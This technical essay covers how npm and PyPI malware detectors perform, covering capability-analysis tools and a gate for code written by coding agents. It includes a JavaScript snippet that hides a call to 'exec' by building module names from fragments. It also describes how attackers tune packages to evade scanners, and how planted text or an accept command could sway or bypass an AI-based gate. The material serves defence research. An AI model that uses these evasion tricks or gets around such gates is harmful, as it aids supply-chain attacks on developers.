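Taint tracking follows data through a program. The analyst defines sources, such as secrets, and sinks, such as network calls, and the tool reports any path from one to the other. Here it would follow the value of `NPM_TOKEN` into `token`, then `body`, and report that it reaches the network request. A package that reads a port number and separately downloads a font would not trigger the rule. But a legitimate publishing tool also sends this token over the network, to npm itself, so the analyst still has to check the destination. The tool can also miss a leak. If the attacker's code used a shell to run `curl` with the token, the shell would read the variable, and the JavaScript would contain no path from source to sink.

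A trained classifier converts each package into a list of numbers, such as how many network calls it makes or how many encoded strings it contains. It learns from packages labelled harmless or malicious which combinations are typical of malware. The four lines above would give it little evidence of malware, because many harmless packages could also use one environment variable, make one network call and contain no encoded text.

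A language model can use the meaning of names in the code. It may flag that a library for making PDFs shouldn't need a publishing token, and that an address called "stats" is an odd place to send one. This comes closer to judging the code's purpose than the other methods do. But the attacker chooses the names and comments, and can add text meant to influence the model.

Two real PyPI packages show why it is difficult to separate harmless code from malicious code with pattern rules. The harmless package `gen_wrappers` fetches an image from a server on the same machine and encodes it as text. The malicious package `gmgeoip` reads a system file that lists user accounts, encodes it in the same way and sends it to an outside address. The two packages use some of the same functions in a similar order, and *Cutting the Gordian Knot* (Guo, Liu and colleagues, 2026) reports that three popular detectors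 flagged the harmless one as malware. Taint tracking could in principle detect that the data travels in opposite directions in the two packages.

### How 11 npm detectors compared

In *How Effective Are NPM Malicious Package Detectors?*, a separate study for the ASE 2026 software engineering conference, Guo, Liu and colleagues (2026) ran 11 detectors on the same npm packages. They used 6,420 malicious package versions, mostly published between 2021 and 2025, and 7,288 harmless packages from among the registry's most downloaded.

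Precision is the share of flagged packages that really are malicious, and recall is the share of malicious packages that the detector flags. F1 combines them as their harmonic mean:

F1 = 2 × precision × recall / (precision + recall)

Because of this formula, a detector needs both high precision and high recall to get a high F1. The following results are a selection.

| Detector | Method | Precision | Recall | F1 |
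|---|---|---|---|---|
| Packj, static mode | Flags any of 56 sensitive calls | 50.41% | 98.69% | 66.73% |
| OSSGadget | Pattern rules | 50.41% | 91.56% | 65.02% |
| GuardDog | Pattern rules and taint tracking | 96.99% | 89.92% | 93.32% |
| GENIE | Data-flow queries | 99.76% | 46.14% | 63.10% |
| SAP, decision tree | Trained classifier | 99.88% | 65.62% | 79.21% |
| ProfMal | Trained classifier | 97.55% | 77.45% | 86.34% |
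| SocketAI, rebuilt | Language model | 98.21% | 44.41% | 61.16% |
| IntelGuard | Language model with known cases | 98.24% | 93.82% | 95.98% |

Guo and colleagues attribute the spread to how each detector handles the capability-intent gap. Packj treats a capability as enough to flag a package, so it missed almost no malware but also flagged 6,234 of the 7,288 harmless packages. GENIE requires much stronger evidence. One of its queries matches only when at least three kinds of system information flow to the same web request, so it misses malware that steals only one or two.

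Guo and colleagues credit taint tracking for GuardDog's good balance. Their own breakdown makes this doubtful, because two of GuardDog's 22 rules produced over 90% of its detections. One detects install script abuse and the other suspicious web addresses, and neither sounds much like taint tracking. GuardDog also has a list of legitimate install commands that it ignores, which may explain much of its precision.

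The researchers' method of confirming malicious packages may also have favoured GuardDog and OSSGadget. Three experts reviewed each candidate package, but only at the places that at least one of these tools had flagged. If both tools missed the malicious code, the experts could have discarded the package as mislabelled, inflating the two tools' measured recall.

The averages mostly reflect one style of attack, in which a package collects information about the machine and sends it out. GuardDog caught more than 94% of packages that sent data out, but only 7% of those that built and ran new code at runtime. IntelGuard scored 98.5% on packages that steal data and 62.5% on packages that inject content into web pages.

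### Attacks outside the code files

In 1,362 of the malicious packages (21.2%), the attack was entirely in the install scripts, with no malicious code in any JavaScript file. The commands for these scripts are in `package.json`, which also lists the package's name, version and dependencies. A detector that reads only JavaScript files will miss such an attack, however good its rules are.

GuardDog must have caught more than half of these 1,362 packages, which Guo and colleagues call structurally undetectable by tools that analyse code. It missed 647 malicious packages in total, so this holds even if every one it missed was of this kind. GuardDog looks at install commands, so detection depends partly on which files a tool reads.

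However, an install script's command may only run another file, and legitimate tools such as Prisma and husky also use install scripts. The study cites an estimate that 2.2% of npm packages declare them. In a registry of about 3.57 million packages, a scanner that flagged every install script would flag nearly 80,000 packages, most of them presumably harmless.

Users can block install scripts with npm's `--ignore-scripts` option instead of judging them. Poireault (2026), in *GitHub to Update npm to Thwart Software Supply Chain Attacks*, reported in June that a new version of npm would disable install scripts. Blocking these scripts removes the attacker's easiest opportunity, but malicious code can still run when a program loads the package.

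### Why trained classifiers get worse

Several trained classifiers did much worse on newer malware. The decision-tree version of SAP caught 87% of the malicious packages from 2021 and 39% of those from 2023. Cerebro, which uses a small language model trained on sequences of program behaviour, caught 77% of the malicious packages from 2022 and 27% of those from 2024 and 2025.

Guo and colleagues found that malware had become simpler. The average malicious package made 12.5 sensitive calls in 2021 and 6.8 in 2023. Many attackers stopped collecting a long list of system details and instead ran a single shell command. Classifiers that relied on encoded text and long chains of suspicious calls therefore had little left to detect.

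PyPI shows a similar decline. In *MALGUARD*, Gao, Sun and colleagues (2025) trained classifiers on malware from 2021 and 2022. One, which used the common XGBoost method, had a recall of 80.3% on malware from those years and 53.4% on malware from 2024.

Trained classifiers need regular retraining, much as rules need regular updates. In *One Detector Fits All*, Montaruli, Compagna and colleagues (2025) retrained a classifier for PyPI by adding 80 days of recent packages to its training data. It then detected 180 of 216 known malicious releases, up from 153, with about the same number of false alarms. Guo and colleagues conclude that rules can adapt through maintenance in a way that trained classifiers fundamentally cannot, but this goes beyond their evidence because they ran fixed versions of the tools and did not retrain the classifiers.

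### Language models as code readers

SocketAI and IntelGuard ran on the same language model, GPT-4.1 mini, yet their recall differed by 49 percentage points. SocketAI prompts the model for an initial report, a critique of that report, and then a final report. According to Guo and colleagues, the critique often led the model to drop correct detections. SocketAI also skipped files beyond the first 20 and scored some real malware just below its cut-off.

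IntelGuard divides the package into pieces, and the model assesses each one using similar cases from a collection built from more than 8,000 reports on earlier attacks. The researchers plausibly consider this evidence the decisive difference, but the file limit and the self-criticism also differed, so the comparison cannot isolate the effect of the lookup. If some of the reports describe attacks in the test set, IntelGuard's result overstates how well it handles new malware. The researchers rebuilt SocketAI from its published description, so the commercial service from the security company Socket may perform better.

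The prompt makes a large difference as well. Ryan, Khalil and colleagues (2026), in *An Evaluation of Large Language Models for Detection of Malicious Python Packages*, tested 13 models, mostly fairly small open ones. Average F1 ranged from 0.40 to 0.99 across models, and most errors were false positives. Across all models, F1 averaged 0.74 with a plain request but only 0.23 with a prompt that included worked examples. The detection test used just 103 files, 10 of them malicious, so the exact scores mean little. It still makes sense to test a model with the prompt that the gate will use.

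File size is a more basic problem, because a model can read only a limited amount of text at once. In June 2026, attackers compromised `ai-sdk-ollama`, an npm package with more than 100,000 weekly downloads, and hid their code in it as a list of more than 1.3 million numbers. The file was 4.5 megabytes, too large for many models to read at once.

In *CASHEWS*, Noirot Ferrand, Adei and colleagues (2026) tested detectors using newer models, including GPT-5.6 Luna and DeepSeek V4 Flash, on 512 large npm files. All four authors work at Socket. Each file had more than 25,000 tokens (the short pieces of text that a model processes), and the detectors could analyse only 69% to 86% of the files. With unread files counted as harmless, the detectors missed 28% to 40% of the malicious files and had false-positive rates of at most 1.2%.

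The researchers then decoded hidden text, cut irrelevant code and, if a file was still too large, sent only its three most suspicious parts to the model. The detectors could now analyse nearly every file and missed 16% to 22% of the malicious ones. False positives rose to as much as 2.9%. Some of the remaining misses were large bundles of code whose harmful part was not among the three selected.

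If a gate counts unread files as harmless, attackers can get past it by making a file bigger. A gate can prevent this by holding unread files for review, but large files are often harmless. Of the 512 large files in the test, 346 were harmless, even though half of the full collection was malicious.

### What happens when attackers expect a scan

In the npm study, Guo and colleagues found no evasion techniques, such as encoding text to hide it or deleting traces afterwards, in 80.3% of the malicious packages. They attribute this to the lack of scanning before publication, which allowed simple attacks to work, but they did not test that explanation. The sample also included only malware that had already been caught, so well-hidden malware is probably underrepresented.

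On July 28, 2026, npm began scanning new packages before they become installable, according to GitHub's *npm publish-time malware scanning and dual-use metadata* (2026). After the scan, npm can publish a package, hold it for manual review or block it. GitHub promises only to block "the malware we can detect". In *NPM Implements Pre-Publication Malware Scanning, But Will It Work?*, OpenSourceMalware welcomes the change but is sceptical about the results, because it argues that GitHub's existing technology lets hundreds of malicious packages stay published each day.

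If everyone scans packages, simple attacks should fail more often, and the remaining attackers will have a reason to test their packages against scanners first. The npm study's recall figures may then be too high, since they are based mostly on packages from attackers who weren't trying to hide.

To test deliberate evasion, Montaruli and colleagues rewrote malicious Python packages without changing what the packages did, for example by encoding addresses, splitting up strings or calling functions in unusual ways. A program tried changes and kept those that lowered the detector's score. With the false-positive rate fixed at 1%, the share of malicious packages their best detector caught fell from 95% to 24%. After they added rewritten packages to its training data, it caught 87% of a new batch made with the same kinds of changes. The experiment doesn't show how the retrained detector would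 do against a technique missing from its training data.

An attacker can run a public tool such as GuardDog privately as often as they like. A registry's scanner is harder to study because the attacker learns only whether the registry accepted the package, and GitHub may act against the account that uploaded it. Keeping some rules and scores private could therefore slow attackers.

Attackers may find it easier to evade scanners with ordinary-looking code than with heavy disguise. Guo and colleagues found that packages with four or more evasion techniques were caught by more detectors than packages with fewer, because heavy disguise is itself suspicious. A short install command that downloads the harmful part later leaves much less to scan. The share of malware that used install scripts to evade code scanners rose from 2.9% in 2023 to 9.4% in 2024 and 2025, before npm's new scan began.

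### False alarms at the scale of a registry

Even a fairly accurate detector can produce far more false alarms than detections when malware is rare. PyPI introduced malware scanning in 2020 and dropped it two years later because of the number of false positives.

Montaruli and colleagues collected 91,949 new PyPI releases over 37 days in the spring of 2025, about 2,485 a day. On its strictest practical setting, which allowed a false-positive rate of at most 0.1%, their classifier found 92 malicious releases, or about 2.5 a day. Since nearly all releases are harmless, the expected number of false alarms is roughly the daily total multiplied by the false-positive rate:

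- at 5%, 2,485 × 0.05 ≈ 124 false alarms a day
- at 0.1%, 2,485 × 0.001 ≈ 2.5 false alarms a day

At a false-positive rate of 5%, reviewers would face about 124 false alarms a day to find a handful of malicious releases. At 0.1%, roughly half the alerts are real, but the same classifier misses more malware.

| Maximum false-positive rate | False alarms per day | Known malicious releases caught, of 216 | Share of alerts that were real |
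|---|---|---|---|
| 30% | 743 | 208 | 0.8% |
| 10% | 247 | 196 | 2.1% |
| 1% | 21 | 180 | 18.7% |
| 0.1% | 2.2 | 92 | 53.2% |
| 0.05% | 0.9 | 77 | 68.8% |

At 0.1%, the classifier missed 124 of the 216 known malicious releases. Montaruli and colleagues argue that this setting fits the roughly 20 minutes a week that PyPI's maintainers have for reviewing alerts. At a minute per alert, they estimate that false alerts would take about 15 minutes a week. But reviewers can't tell false alerts from real ones beforehand, so they have to review both, which would take about 33 minutes.

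The 216 releases are a lower bound on the malware present. They include only what public databases listed or the detectors found, and the study counts everything else as harmless. If any malware went undetected, the classifier's true recall was lower than the table's figure. At least 0.23% of the releases were malicious. Gao and colleagues found 113 malicious packages among 64,348 new uploads to PyPI, or 0.18%, which also leaves out anything their detector missed.

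Base rates also affect the npm results, because high precision is much easier to achieve when nearly half the packages tested are malicious. IntelGuard flagged 108 of the 7,288 harmless packages, or about 1.5%. If its error rates were the same on PyPI, it would raise about 37 false alarms a day, and only around 13% of its alerts would be real, compared with 98% in the test. This estimate is rough, partly because Guo and colleagues used popular packages, which tend to trigger more false alarms than typical ones.

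The same calculation can change which combination of detectors looks best. Guo and colleagues suggest screening every package with GuardDog, which takes about 2.5 seconds per package, and giving only the flagged ones to a language model. With IntelGuard as the second step, a package fails only if both tools flag it. That combination had an F1 of 92.4% in the test, lower than either tool alone, but it flagged only about 0.4% of harmless packages. At PyPI's volume, that would mean roughly 10 false alarms a day, and about a third of all alerts would be real. A registry with few reviewers might well prefer this combination.

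A company checks far fewer packages than a registry does, so it can accept a higher false-positive rate. Montaruli and colleagues ran their classifier on the 1,596 releases of one software company's Python dependencies over the same 37 days. They used the 10% setting, which had caught 196 of the 216 known malicious releases on PyPI. The classifier raised 46 false alarms, about 1.2 a day. None of the dependencies came under attack during that period, so the test could not measure how many attacks the company would have caught.

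A gate for a coding agent is in a similar position, but it may raise several alarms at once. Guo and colleagues cite an estimate that an average npm package implicitly trusts 79 others. If an agent's request brought in 79 unchecked packages, a gate with the company test's alarm rate of about 2.9% would raise two or three false alarms on average before the agent could continue.

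## Working out what code can do without running it

Capability analysis lists the kinds of access a piece of code could use. The list alone is a poor way to detect malware, as Packj's many false alarms in the npm study showed. It is more useful when a gate compares it with what the package needs or with what an earlier version could do.

A list of the sensitive calls in a package's own files would also be incomplete, because the package can make such calls through the other packages it uses. More thorough tools therefore follow calls from function to function.

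### Following the calls

Most code can't open a file or a network connection by itself. It has to call a function in the standard library, which is the code that comes with the programming language. This gives the analysis a place to start:

1. Label the standard-library functions that reach outside the program, for example "files" for a function that reads a file.
2. Build the call graph, which records which functions may call which others.
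3. Give each function the labels of every function it may call, and repeat until a full round changes nothing.
4. Report each package's labels, with a chain of calls that leads to each one.

If L(f) is the set of labels given to function f in the first step, the third step finds the smallest sets C that satisfy

C(f) = L(f) ∪ C(g₁) ∪ C(g₂) ∪ …

where g₁, g₂ and so on are the functions that f may call. The process always ends, even if functions call each other in a circle, because the sets only grow and there are a limited number of labels.

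Suppose the invoice page prints dates with a small library, which has just gone from version 2.1 to 2.2. This is the invented call graph of the new version:

```
Format        ->  parseLayout, zoneOffset
parseLayout   ->  strings.Split
zoneOffset    ->  os.ReadFile, refreshZones
refreshZones  ->  http.Get
```

Version 2.1 had no `refreshZones`, and its `zoneOffset` only read the computer's time-zone file, so the whole library had one label, "files". In version 2.2, the labels spread as follows.

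| Function | Start | Round 1 | Round 2 | Round 3 |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| `strings.Split` | none | none | none | none |
| `os.ReadFile` | files | files | files | files |
| `http.Get` | network | network | network | network |
| `refreshZones` | none | network | network | network |
| `zoneOffset` | none | files | files, network | files, network |
| `parseLayout` | none | none | none | none |
| `Format` | none | none | files | files, network |

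A fourth round changes nothing, so the analysis stops. The invoice page calls only `Format`, whose own code contains no network call, but the report shows that `Format` can now reach the network through `Format → zoneOffset → refreshZones → http.Get`.

A reviewer can go straight to `refreshZones` instead of reading the whole library. The function may download the latest time-zone rules, which is reasonable for a date library, or it may send data to an attacker. The label is the same in both cases, so the capability-intent gap remains.

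### Capslock for Go

Capslock applies this method to Go programs. Google (2023) released it as a complement to vulnerability management, which doesn't fully show whether a dependency is safe to use.

Capslock labels whole packages first and then makes exceptions for individual functions. In Google's example, everything in Go's `os` package counts as "operating system" by default, but the function that changes a file's owner counts as "files". Capslock stops searching along a path when it reaches a function marked "safe". The labelling is manageable for Go. In a 2026 talk, *using capslock analysis to develop seccomp filters for rust and other services*, Harvey puts the list at roughly 800 functions, about 700 of them marked safe.

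Google's *Examples* shows what Capslock reports for code from a real attack. In August 2022, someone cloned thousands of GitHub repositories and added a malicious function that runs automatically when the program starts. It sent all the environment variables to a server and ran the server's response as a shell command. Capslock found eight capabilities in this short function, including network access and the ability to run other programs.

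When Google ran Capslock on Capslock's own code, it found seven capabilities, six of which were also on the malicious function's list. For example, Capslock can run other programs because it uses a Go library that starts Go's build tool. The malicious function had only two capabilities that Capslock lacked, network access and the ability to change the system's state. A long list is therefore weak evidence of malice, but a reviewer who looked up the malicious function because of its list would see the problem at once.

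Capslock is still under development. Version 0.3.1 includes a command that lists the capabilities added between two revisions of a repository (Google, *capslock*, 2025), and MacPorts had version 0.3.2 by August 2026 (MacPorts, *capslock*).

Prototypes for Rust and Java also exist. Harvey, who works on the Rust prototype at the Rust Foundation, estimates that Rust's standard library has 10,000 to 11,000 functions, too many to label by hand for an experiment. So Harvey ran the library's own tests, recorded the requests they made to the operating system, and guessed the labels from those. Harvey considers this good enough for a prototype but "absolutely insufficient" for production.

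### Cackle for Rust

Cackle is a separate tool for Rust, where packages are called crates. Its configuration file lists what each crate may use, and the check fails if a crate uses anything else. If the date library were a crate, its entry might be:

```toml
[pkg.datefmt]
allow_apis = ["fs"]
```

Here `fs` stands for the file system. Version 2.2 would fail the check because it also uses the network.

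*Making Rust supply chain attacks harder with Cackle* (Lattimore, 2023) describes how Cackle examines a program's compiled pieces as the build produces them and works out which functions refer to which others. It then uses debugging information to trace each reference to a crate. Cackle attributes a capability to the crate that uses the sensitive function directly, whereas Capslock also passes it up to every caller. If the date library had moved its download into a helper crate, Cackle would attribute the download to the helper.

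Cackle ignores code that the finished program can't reach. A program that uses an image library only to encode pictures in memory wouldn't need to give that library permission to access files, even if the library's other functions can save them. Build scripts run while a crate is being compiled and pose much the same risk as npm's install scripts. Cackle also checks each of these scripts before running it, and can then run it in a sandbox.

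Lattimore, who wrote Cackle, tried it on a few popular programs and found that slightly under half of their crates needed no special permissions. Cackle protects best against changes in those crates, because any restricted access would be new. Once a crate has permission to use the network, it can contact any server without Cackle flagging it.

Users also have to classify some functions themselves. Many Rust programs reach the network through a crate called tokio, and another crate could use tokio's network functions unnoticed unless the configuration lists them. cackle-rs' *cargo-acl 0.9.0* says that the tool still runs only on Linux, so it can miss malicious code meant for Windows or macOS, and advises users to assume that a determined attacker can get around the check.

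### malcontent for binaries and scripts

Both of these tools need a program they can build, but malcontent, an open-source tool from the security company Chainguard, can examine almost any file, including binaries, scripts and container images. *malcontent* (2024) describes more than 16,000 YARA rules, which match text and byte patterns. If a rule matches the name of a function that opens connections, for example, malcontent reports a network capability with a risk level.

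A pattern match doesn't show whether the program ever runs the matching code, and malcontent's documentation describes the tool as "a bit paranoid and prone to false positives". The advantage of pattern matching is that it doesn't need the program's source code.

malcontent has reached at least version 1.21.0. releasealert.dev's *chainguard-dev/malcontent* lists vulnerabilities in the scanner itself, including one, now fixed, through which a specially made reference to a container image could make it send login credentials to an attacker's server. A gate opens files from strangers all day, so its analysis tools should run without credentials they don't need.

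| Tool | What it examines | How it finds capabilities |
|---|---|---|
| Capslock | Go source code and its dependencies | Passes labels from library functions up to their callers |
| Cackle | Compiled Rust code, during a build | Finds restricted functions in reachable code and checks each crate's permissions |
| malcontent | Binaries, scripts and container images | Matches text and byte patterns |

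### What Java packages can reach

Rahman, Paramitha and colleagues (2024), in *What's in a Package?*, applied call-graph analysis to packages from Maven, the main package system for Java. One of their motives was Log4Shell, a vulnerability disclosed in December 2021 in the logging library log4j. An attacker could use the library's lookup feature, which was on by default, to load an object from a website. Most developers didn't know the feature existed.

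The researchers first compiled a list of sensitive functions, taking candidates from Java's documentation, the fixes for 255 known vulnerabilities in the packages they studied, and published examples of common weaknesses. The final list had 227 functions in 15 groups. To check it, they compared it with 11 functions that several earlier studies had agreed were sensitive. Their process had found nine, and they added a tenth afterwards. They did not measure how many of the listed functions don't belong there, and the list is certainly broad. For example, writing a log message counts as file output.

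They then chose 45 widely used packages, such as web frameworks and JSON parsers. With all their dependencies, these came to 1,210 packages and 30,772 versions. About half of the versions (50.2%) called no listed function in their own code. Versions of the 45 main packages averaged 72 calls to listed functions in their own code and another 168 in their dependencies. A gate that checks only the package an agent asked for would therefore miss most of the sensitive calls.

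Packages with similar jobs varied widely in how many of the listed functions they called. Among libraries for dependency injection (connecting the parts of a program), dagger called none, guice called 22 different ones, and spring-context called 53 from 10 of the 15 groups. Some differences came from extra features and others from how the packages were built. Rahman and colleagues stress that more calls do not mean more risk.

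The results only moderately support the idea that a capability list would have exposed Log4Shell. The list includes functions of the kind that log4j's lookup used. But the analysis found 55 different sensitive functions in a recent version of log4j's main package, so a developer could easily have overlooked the important one.

In a survey, the researchers showed developers a chart of the sensitive functions in a package they used and in its alternatives. Of the 110 who responded, 44.6% said they would consider this information when choosing a dependency, and 41.8% said it wouldn't have changed their decision. The 44.6% includes the 19.1% of respondents who would simply pick the package with the fewest sensitive calls, a rule the study doesn't support. One respondent was surprised that a JSON parser used the network. Only 1.4% of the developers contacted replied, and the question was hypothetical,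 so the survey is weak evidence of what developers in general would do.

### Access that the program never uses

Call-graph analysis often reports things a program will not do, partly because it assumes that every branch of the code can run. Google's *Caveats* describes a function that reads a file only if one of its inputs is `true`. Capslock gives the "files" label to every caller of that function, even one that always passes `false`.

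Harvey demonstrated this with a tiny program that reformats JSON text. The static analysis reported that the program could read system state, because it included debugging code that looks up the user's language in an environment variable. When Harvey ran the program, that code never executed, and the recorded list of capabilities was empty.

Interfaces can also lead an analysis to report access that a program may not use. An interface lets code work with several kinds of object in the same way. In Java, a line that writes to an "output stream" may be writing to a file, a network connection or a block of memory, depending on which object it receives at run time. A cautious analysis assumes the line could write to any of them.

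Rahman and colleagues measured part of this effect on 34 packages and their dependencies. They compared a method that considers every matching type with a stricter one that considers only the types that reachable code creates. The stricter method removed 39.3% of the calls in the graph but kept 97.4% of the findings that a given package calls a given sensitive function. Broad interfaces therefore made the graph much larger without adding many capabilities. Both methods assume that every branch can run, so the true excess of findings may be much larger than 2.6%.

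The choice of what to analyse can matter more. deps.dev's *golang.org/x/text* shows Capslock's results for a Go library that handles text in different languages. The results include network access and running other programs, which text handling shouldn't need. This is probably because the library comes with tools for its own developers, for example to download character tables, and the analysis covers those too. A gate would get a more relevant result by starting the analysis from the functions the agent's code calls.

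Labels can also be too coarse. Harvey considers this true of the current set, because the "Files" label covers both a PDF library that writes to the project folder and malware that reads saved passwords.

### Access that the analysis misses

A call graph can also omit calls that the program does make. These two lines of JavaScript run a shell command:

```javascript
const name = ["child", "process"].join("_");
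require(name)["ex" + "ec"](command);
```

The first line builds the string `child_process`, the name of Node.js's module for starting programs. The second loads the module and calls its `exec` function. Neither name appears whole in the code, so a simple analysis finds no call to `exec`. A better analysis might work out these strings, but not a name that arrives over the network.

Reflection causes the same problem in Java and Go. It lets a program look up and call functions by name while it runs, and the name may come from a settings file. Capslock also can't analyse native libraries written in C or assembly language. No static analysis can examine code that the program will download later. In the attack from 2022, Capslock could report that the function used the network and started a shell, but it couldn't examine the server's reply, which did not exist yet.

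Capslock reports most of these blind spots as capabilities. It has separate labels for reflection, running other programs, calling C code and operations that bypass Go's safety rules. An "unanalyzed" label covers paths the tool could not follow. The labels show the user that the list of capabilities may be incomplete. Similarly, Cackle requires permission for Rust's `unsafe` code, which can do things the compiler doesn't check.

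But many harmless packages get these labels too. Reflection was the most common group in the Maven study, with calls in 28 of the 34 packages compared. McClintock and Dethridge report in *Bringing Capslock analysis to deps.dev* that 9% of Go packages can run other programs through a dependency. Lattimore's crates needed `unsafe` far more often than any other permission. Blocking every package with a blind spot would stop a lot of ordinary software, so it may be better for a gate to send these packages to a trial run or give them tighter limits.

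The chain of calls can sometimes show whether a reported capability is a concern. When Harvey analysed the server behind crates.io, Rust's package registry, the result included "arbitrary execution". The chain led to a small crate that sets the times on files. The crate made a request directly to the operating system to avoid a bug in a standard C library, but ordinary file access would have allowed the same request.

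Other omissions produce no label. Certain timing errors in Go programs can, in principle, lead to any behaviour, and Capslock doesn't report them. Capslock also analyses the code for one operating system at a time, so a malicious file included only in the Windows version won't appear in a Linux analysis.

Missing pieces of a program can hide calls too. In the Maven study, the number of calls to web functions fell from about 15,000 to 4,400 when the researchers added dependencies to the graph, although more code should mean more calls. Many of the calls went through interfaces that a separate web server implements, and the tool left out a call when no implementation was present. The tools also made mistakes. When Rahman and colleagues compared two of them on the packages' own code, each missed sensitive calls that the other found, 106 in one case and 32 in the other. The tools agreed closely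 on which packages used the most sensitive functions. This supports using them to compare packages, but gives less support to a rule about one particular call.

### What changed since the last version

Many of these problems matter less when a gate compares two versions of the same package. If the date library has always appeared to use reflection, that label is in both versions' lists, so the comparison leaves it out and shows only what changed, such as the new network path.

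McClintock and Dethridge found that fewer than 2% of version updates of Go packages add a capability. At that rate, a company that takes 100 updates a month would have at most about two to review. Most of those would be harmless, since packages also gain capabilities when their developers add features.

*capcheck* (git-pkgs, 2026), a small tool built on Capslock, makes this comparison part of a project's automatic checks. A developer first saves the project's current capabilities in a file. If a new capability later appears, the tool fails the checks and prints the chain of calls behind it. To accept the change, the developer runs an update command and saves the new list.

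The sample configuration for *capcheck* ignores "noisy" capabilities, including files and network, so with that configuration it would not report the date library's new download. Its failure message also includes the command that accepts the change. A coding agent that treats the failure as an error to fix might run that command, so the saved list should be kept where the agent can't change it.

malcontent has a comparison mode as well, and its documentation says this mode can find far subtler attacks than a general scan. Strömberg, in *Detecting the Lottie supply-chain attack with malcontent*, describes a compromised version of Lottie Web Player, a JavaScript library. Compared with the previous version, the file's risk rating went from medium to critical. Strömberg, who started the project, notes that the reviewer still has to decide which changes are reasonable for the library. The documentation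 also uses an attack on the company 3CX as an example. Both are attacks that people already knew about, so they don't show how often the comparison would catch a new one or raise a false alarm. Rahman and colleagues leave the question of whether such differences can identify malicious updates to future research.

A comparison also has to cover code that the program never calls, such as install scripts. In the Axios attack, Datadog found the library's own source unchanged. Even a call graph that included dependencies would have missed the malicious install script, because Axios never called the package that contained it. The gate would have had to treat install scripts as separate starting points, much as Cackle does with build scripts.

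Even a complete comparison can't detect an attacker who stays within the access a package already has. A library for making web requests already uses the network, so code that sends data to the attacker's server adds nothing to the list of what the library can access. Comparing trial runs of the two versions can help, because a trial run records which hosts the code contacts.

The two analyses also have to use the same settings. Capslock's results depend on the operating system, so a list made on a Mac won't match one made on Linux. A new release of the analysis tool may find calls the old one missed, which would look like a change in the package.

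### New code with no earlier version

When an agent edits an existing program, the gate can compare the program before and after. When the agent writes a new script or adds a new page, every capability is new, so the comparison lists all of them. A newly chosen dependency has the same problem, because comparing it with its earlier versions shows how it has changed but not whether this project should accept what it can do. *NodeShield* (Cornelissen and Balliu, 2025), which presents a system for enforcing capability lists in JavaScript, reports that developers had to review less than one capability per dependency update on average, but up to 13 for a new dependency.

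The developer's request is the most direct substitute for the earlier version, though there appear to be no tests of how well any substitute works for agents' code. A request to export invoices as PDF files implies that the new code will read the database and produce a file, but not that it will start a shell or contact a new server. The gate could hold the code if either of those capabilities appeared.

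Someone has to translate the developer's request into a list of expected capabilities, and a language model could do it. The model should see only the request, and should write the list before the agent reads any other text. Otherwise, an instruction planted in a README file could add network access to the list. Requests are also often vague. A model could infer almost nothing from "Make the reports work again" about what access the fix will need. The closest precedent may be work by Gorla and colleagues, cited by Rahman and colleagues, that checked the behaviour of Android apps against their descriptions. However, an app's description is usually longer than a request to an agent, and it covers the whole program.

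The rest of the repository could provide another standard. If the application's other 20 pages read the database and none starts a program, a new page that starts one is unusual. The comparison has to be page by page, because the application as a whole may well start programs already, perhaps in a maintenance script. It works badly for a new kind of task, such as the project's first feature that sends email, and it would allow new pages any excessive access that the existing pages have.

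Comparing a dependency with similar packages seems less promising. In the Maven study, web frameworks used from 0 to 13 of the 15 groups, so there was no normal level to compare with. The differences could still help an agent choose between two packages that both meet the need.

A gate could also start with an empty list of allowed capabilities and require a reason for adding each one. This would suit small scripts, which often need only one or two kinds of access. The reason should come from a person or from the original request, since an agent that someone has misled could write a convincing reason for a capability the script doesn't need.

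Once a person has approved the new code, its list can serve as the baseline for later changes. A tool that automatically saves the list on its first run would accept whatever the agent wrote, including any access the code should not have.

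## What can be proved about code before it runs, and what cannot

Capability analysis can overstate or understate what a program will do. Better tools can reduce both errors, but Rice's theorem (1953) shows that no tool can avoid both for every program. A gate can provide stronger guarantees by accepting only code that is written in a restricted language or comes with a proof. Few of the packages that agents install today meet either condition.

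### Why no analyser is always right

Suppose someone builds an analyser that reads any program and always answers correctly whether it will send the file `invoices.csv` to an outside server. Now take any program P and put it inside a slightly larger one:

```python
simulate(P)    # runs P but discards anything P tries to send
send("invoices.csv", "https://files.example")
```

The larger program reaches its second line, which sends the file, if and only if P finishes. The analyser's answer about the larger program would therefore also show whether P finishes. Alan Turing showed in 1936 that no program can determine this for every P, so the analyser cannot exist.

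Henry Gordon Rice proved the general result, known as Rice's theorem, that no algorithm can decide for every program whether its behaviour has a given property, if some programs have that property and others lack it. The theorem does not cover properties of the program's text, so a scanner can always tell whether a file contains the word `send`, but not always whether the program will send anything.

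The theorem implies that an analyser that always answers yes or no, for arbitrary programs, must sometimes reject a harmless program or accept a harmful one. It doesn't establish how often this must happen, and many individual programs are easy to judge. The analyser's makers can also choose which mistake to avoid. If it rejects every program it can't prove harmless, it will never accept a harmful one, but it will reject some harmless ones. A gate that can hold code for review can also answer "don't know" and leave the decision to a person.

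Real computers have finite memory, so in principle an analyser could check every state the machine can be in. But a single kilobyte of memory has 2^8192 possible states, too many to check in practice.

Fred Cohen applied a similar argument to computer viruses in the 1980s. He defined a virus as a program that modifies other programs to include a copy of itself, possibly altered. Suppose a detector always gives an answer. An attacker can write a program that runs the detector on its own code and infects other programs only if the result is "harmless". If the result is "virus", the program does nothing, so the detector is wrong in both cases. The detector's maker can add a rule for this program, but someone can then write a similar program against the new version. The attacker needs a copy of the detector, so the trick works best against public tools.

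### What a monitor can enforce during a run

A runtime monitor doesn't have to predict what a program will do. With the program above, it can let the simulation run for as long as it takes and intervene only if the program reaches `send`.

Fred Schneider showed in 2000 that if a monitor of this kind sees only the steps of one run so far and can stop the run before the next step, it can enforce only safety properties, which require that some bad thing never happens. A run that breaks a safety property does so at a definite point, and nothing the program does later can undo the violation. "Never send `invoices.csv`" is a safety property, but "close the database connection eventually" is not, because at any point in the run the program might still close it later.

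Information flow isn't a safety property either. Imagine a script that reads a customer's account number and then sends "batch 7 complete" to a logging server. The 7 may be the number of the batch, or it may be a digit of the account number. To find out, one has to ask what the script would have sent if the account number had been different. In its usual form, the requirement is that for every public input x and any two secrets s₁ and s₂,

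output(x, s₁) = output(x, s₂)

where the output is everything an outsider can see. The formula compares two runs, and the monitor sees only one.

A monitor can still prevent many leaks with a stricter rule. One of Schneider's examples is a rule that a program may not send any message after it has read a file. This rule is a safety property, but it also stops a script that reads a secret and then sends something unrelated.

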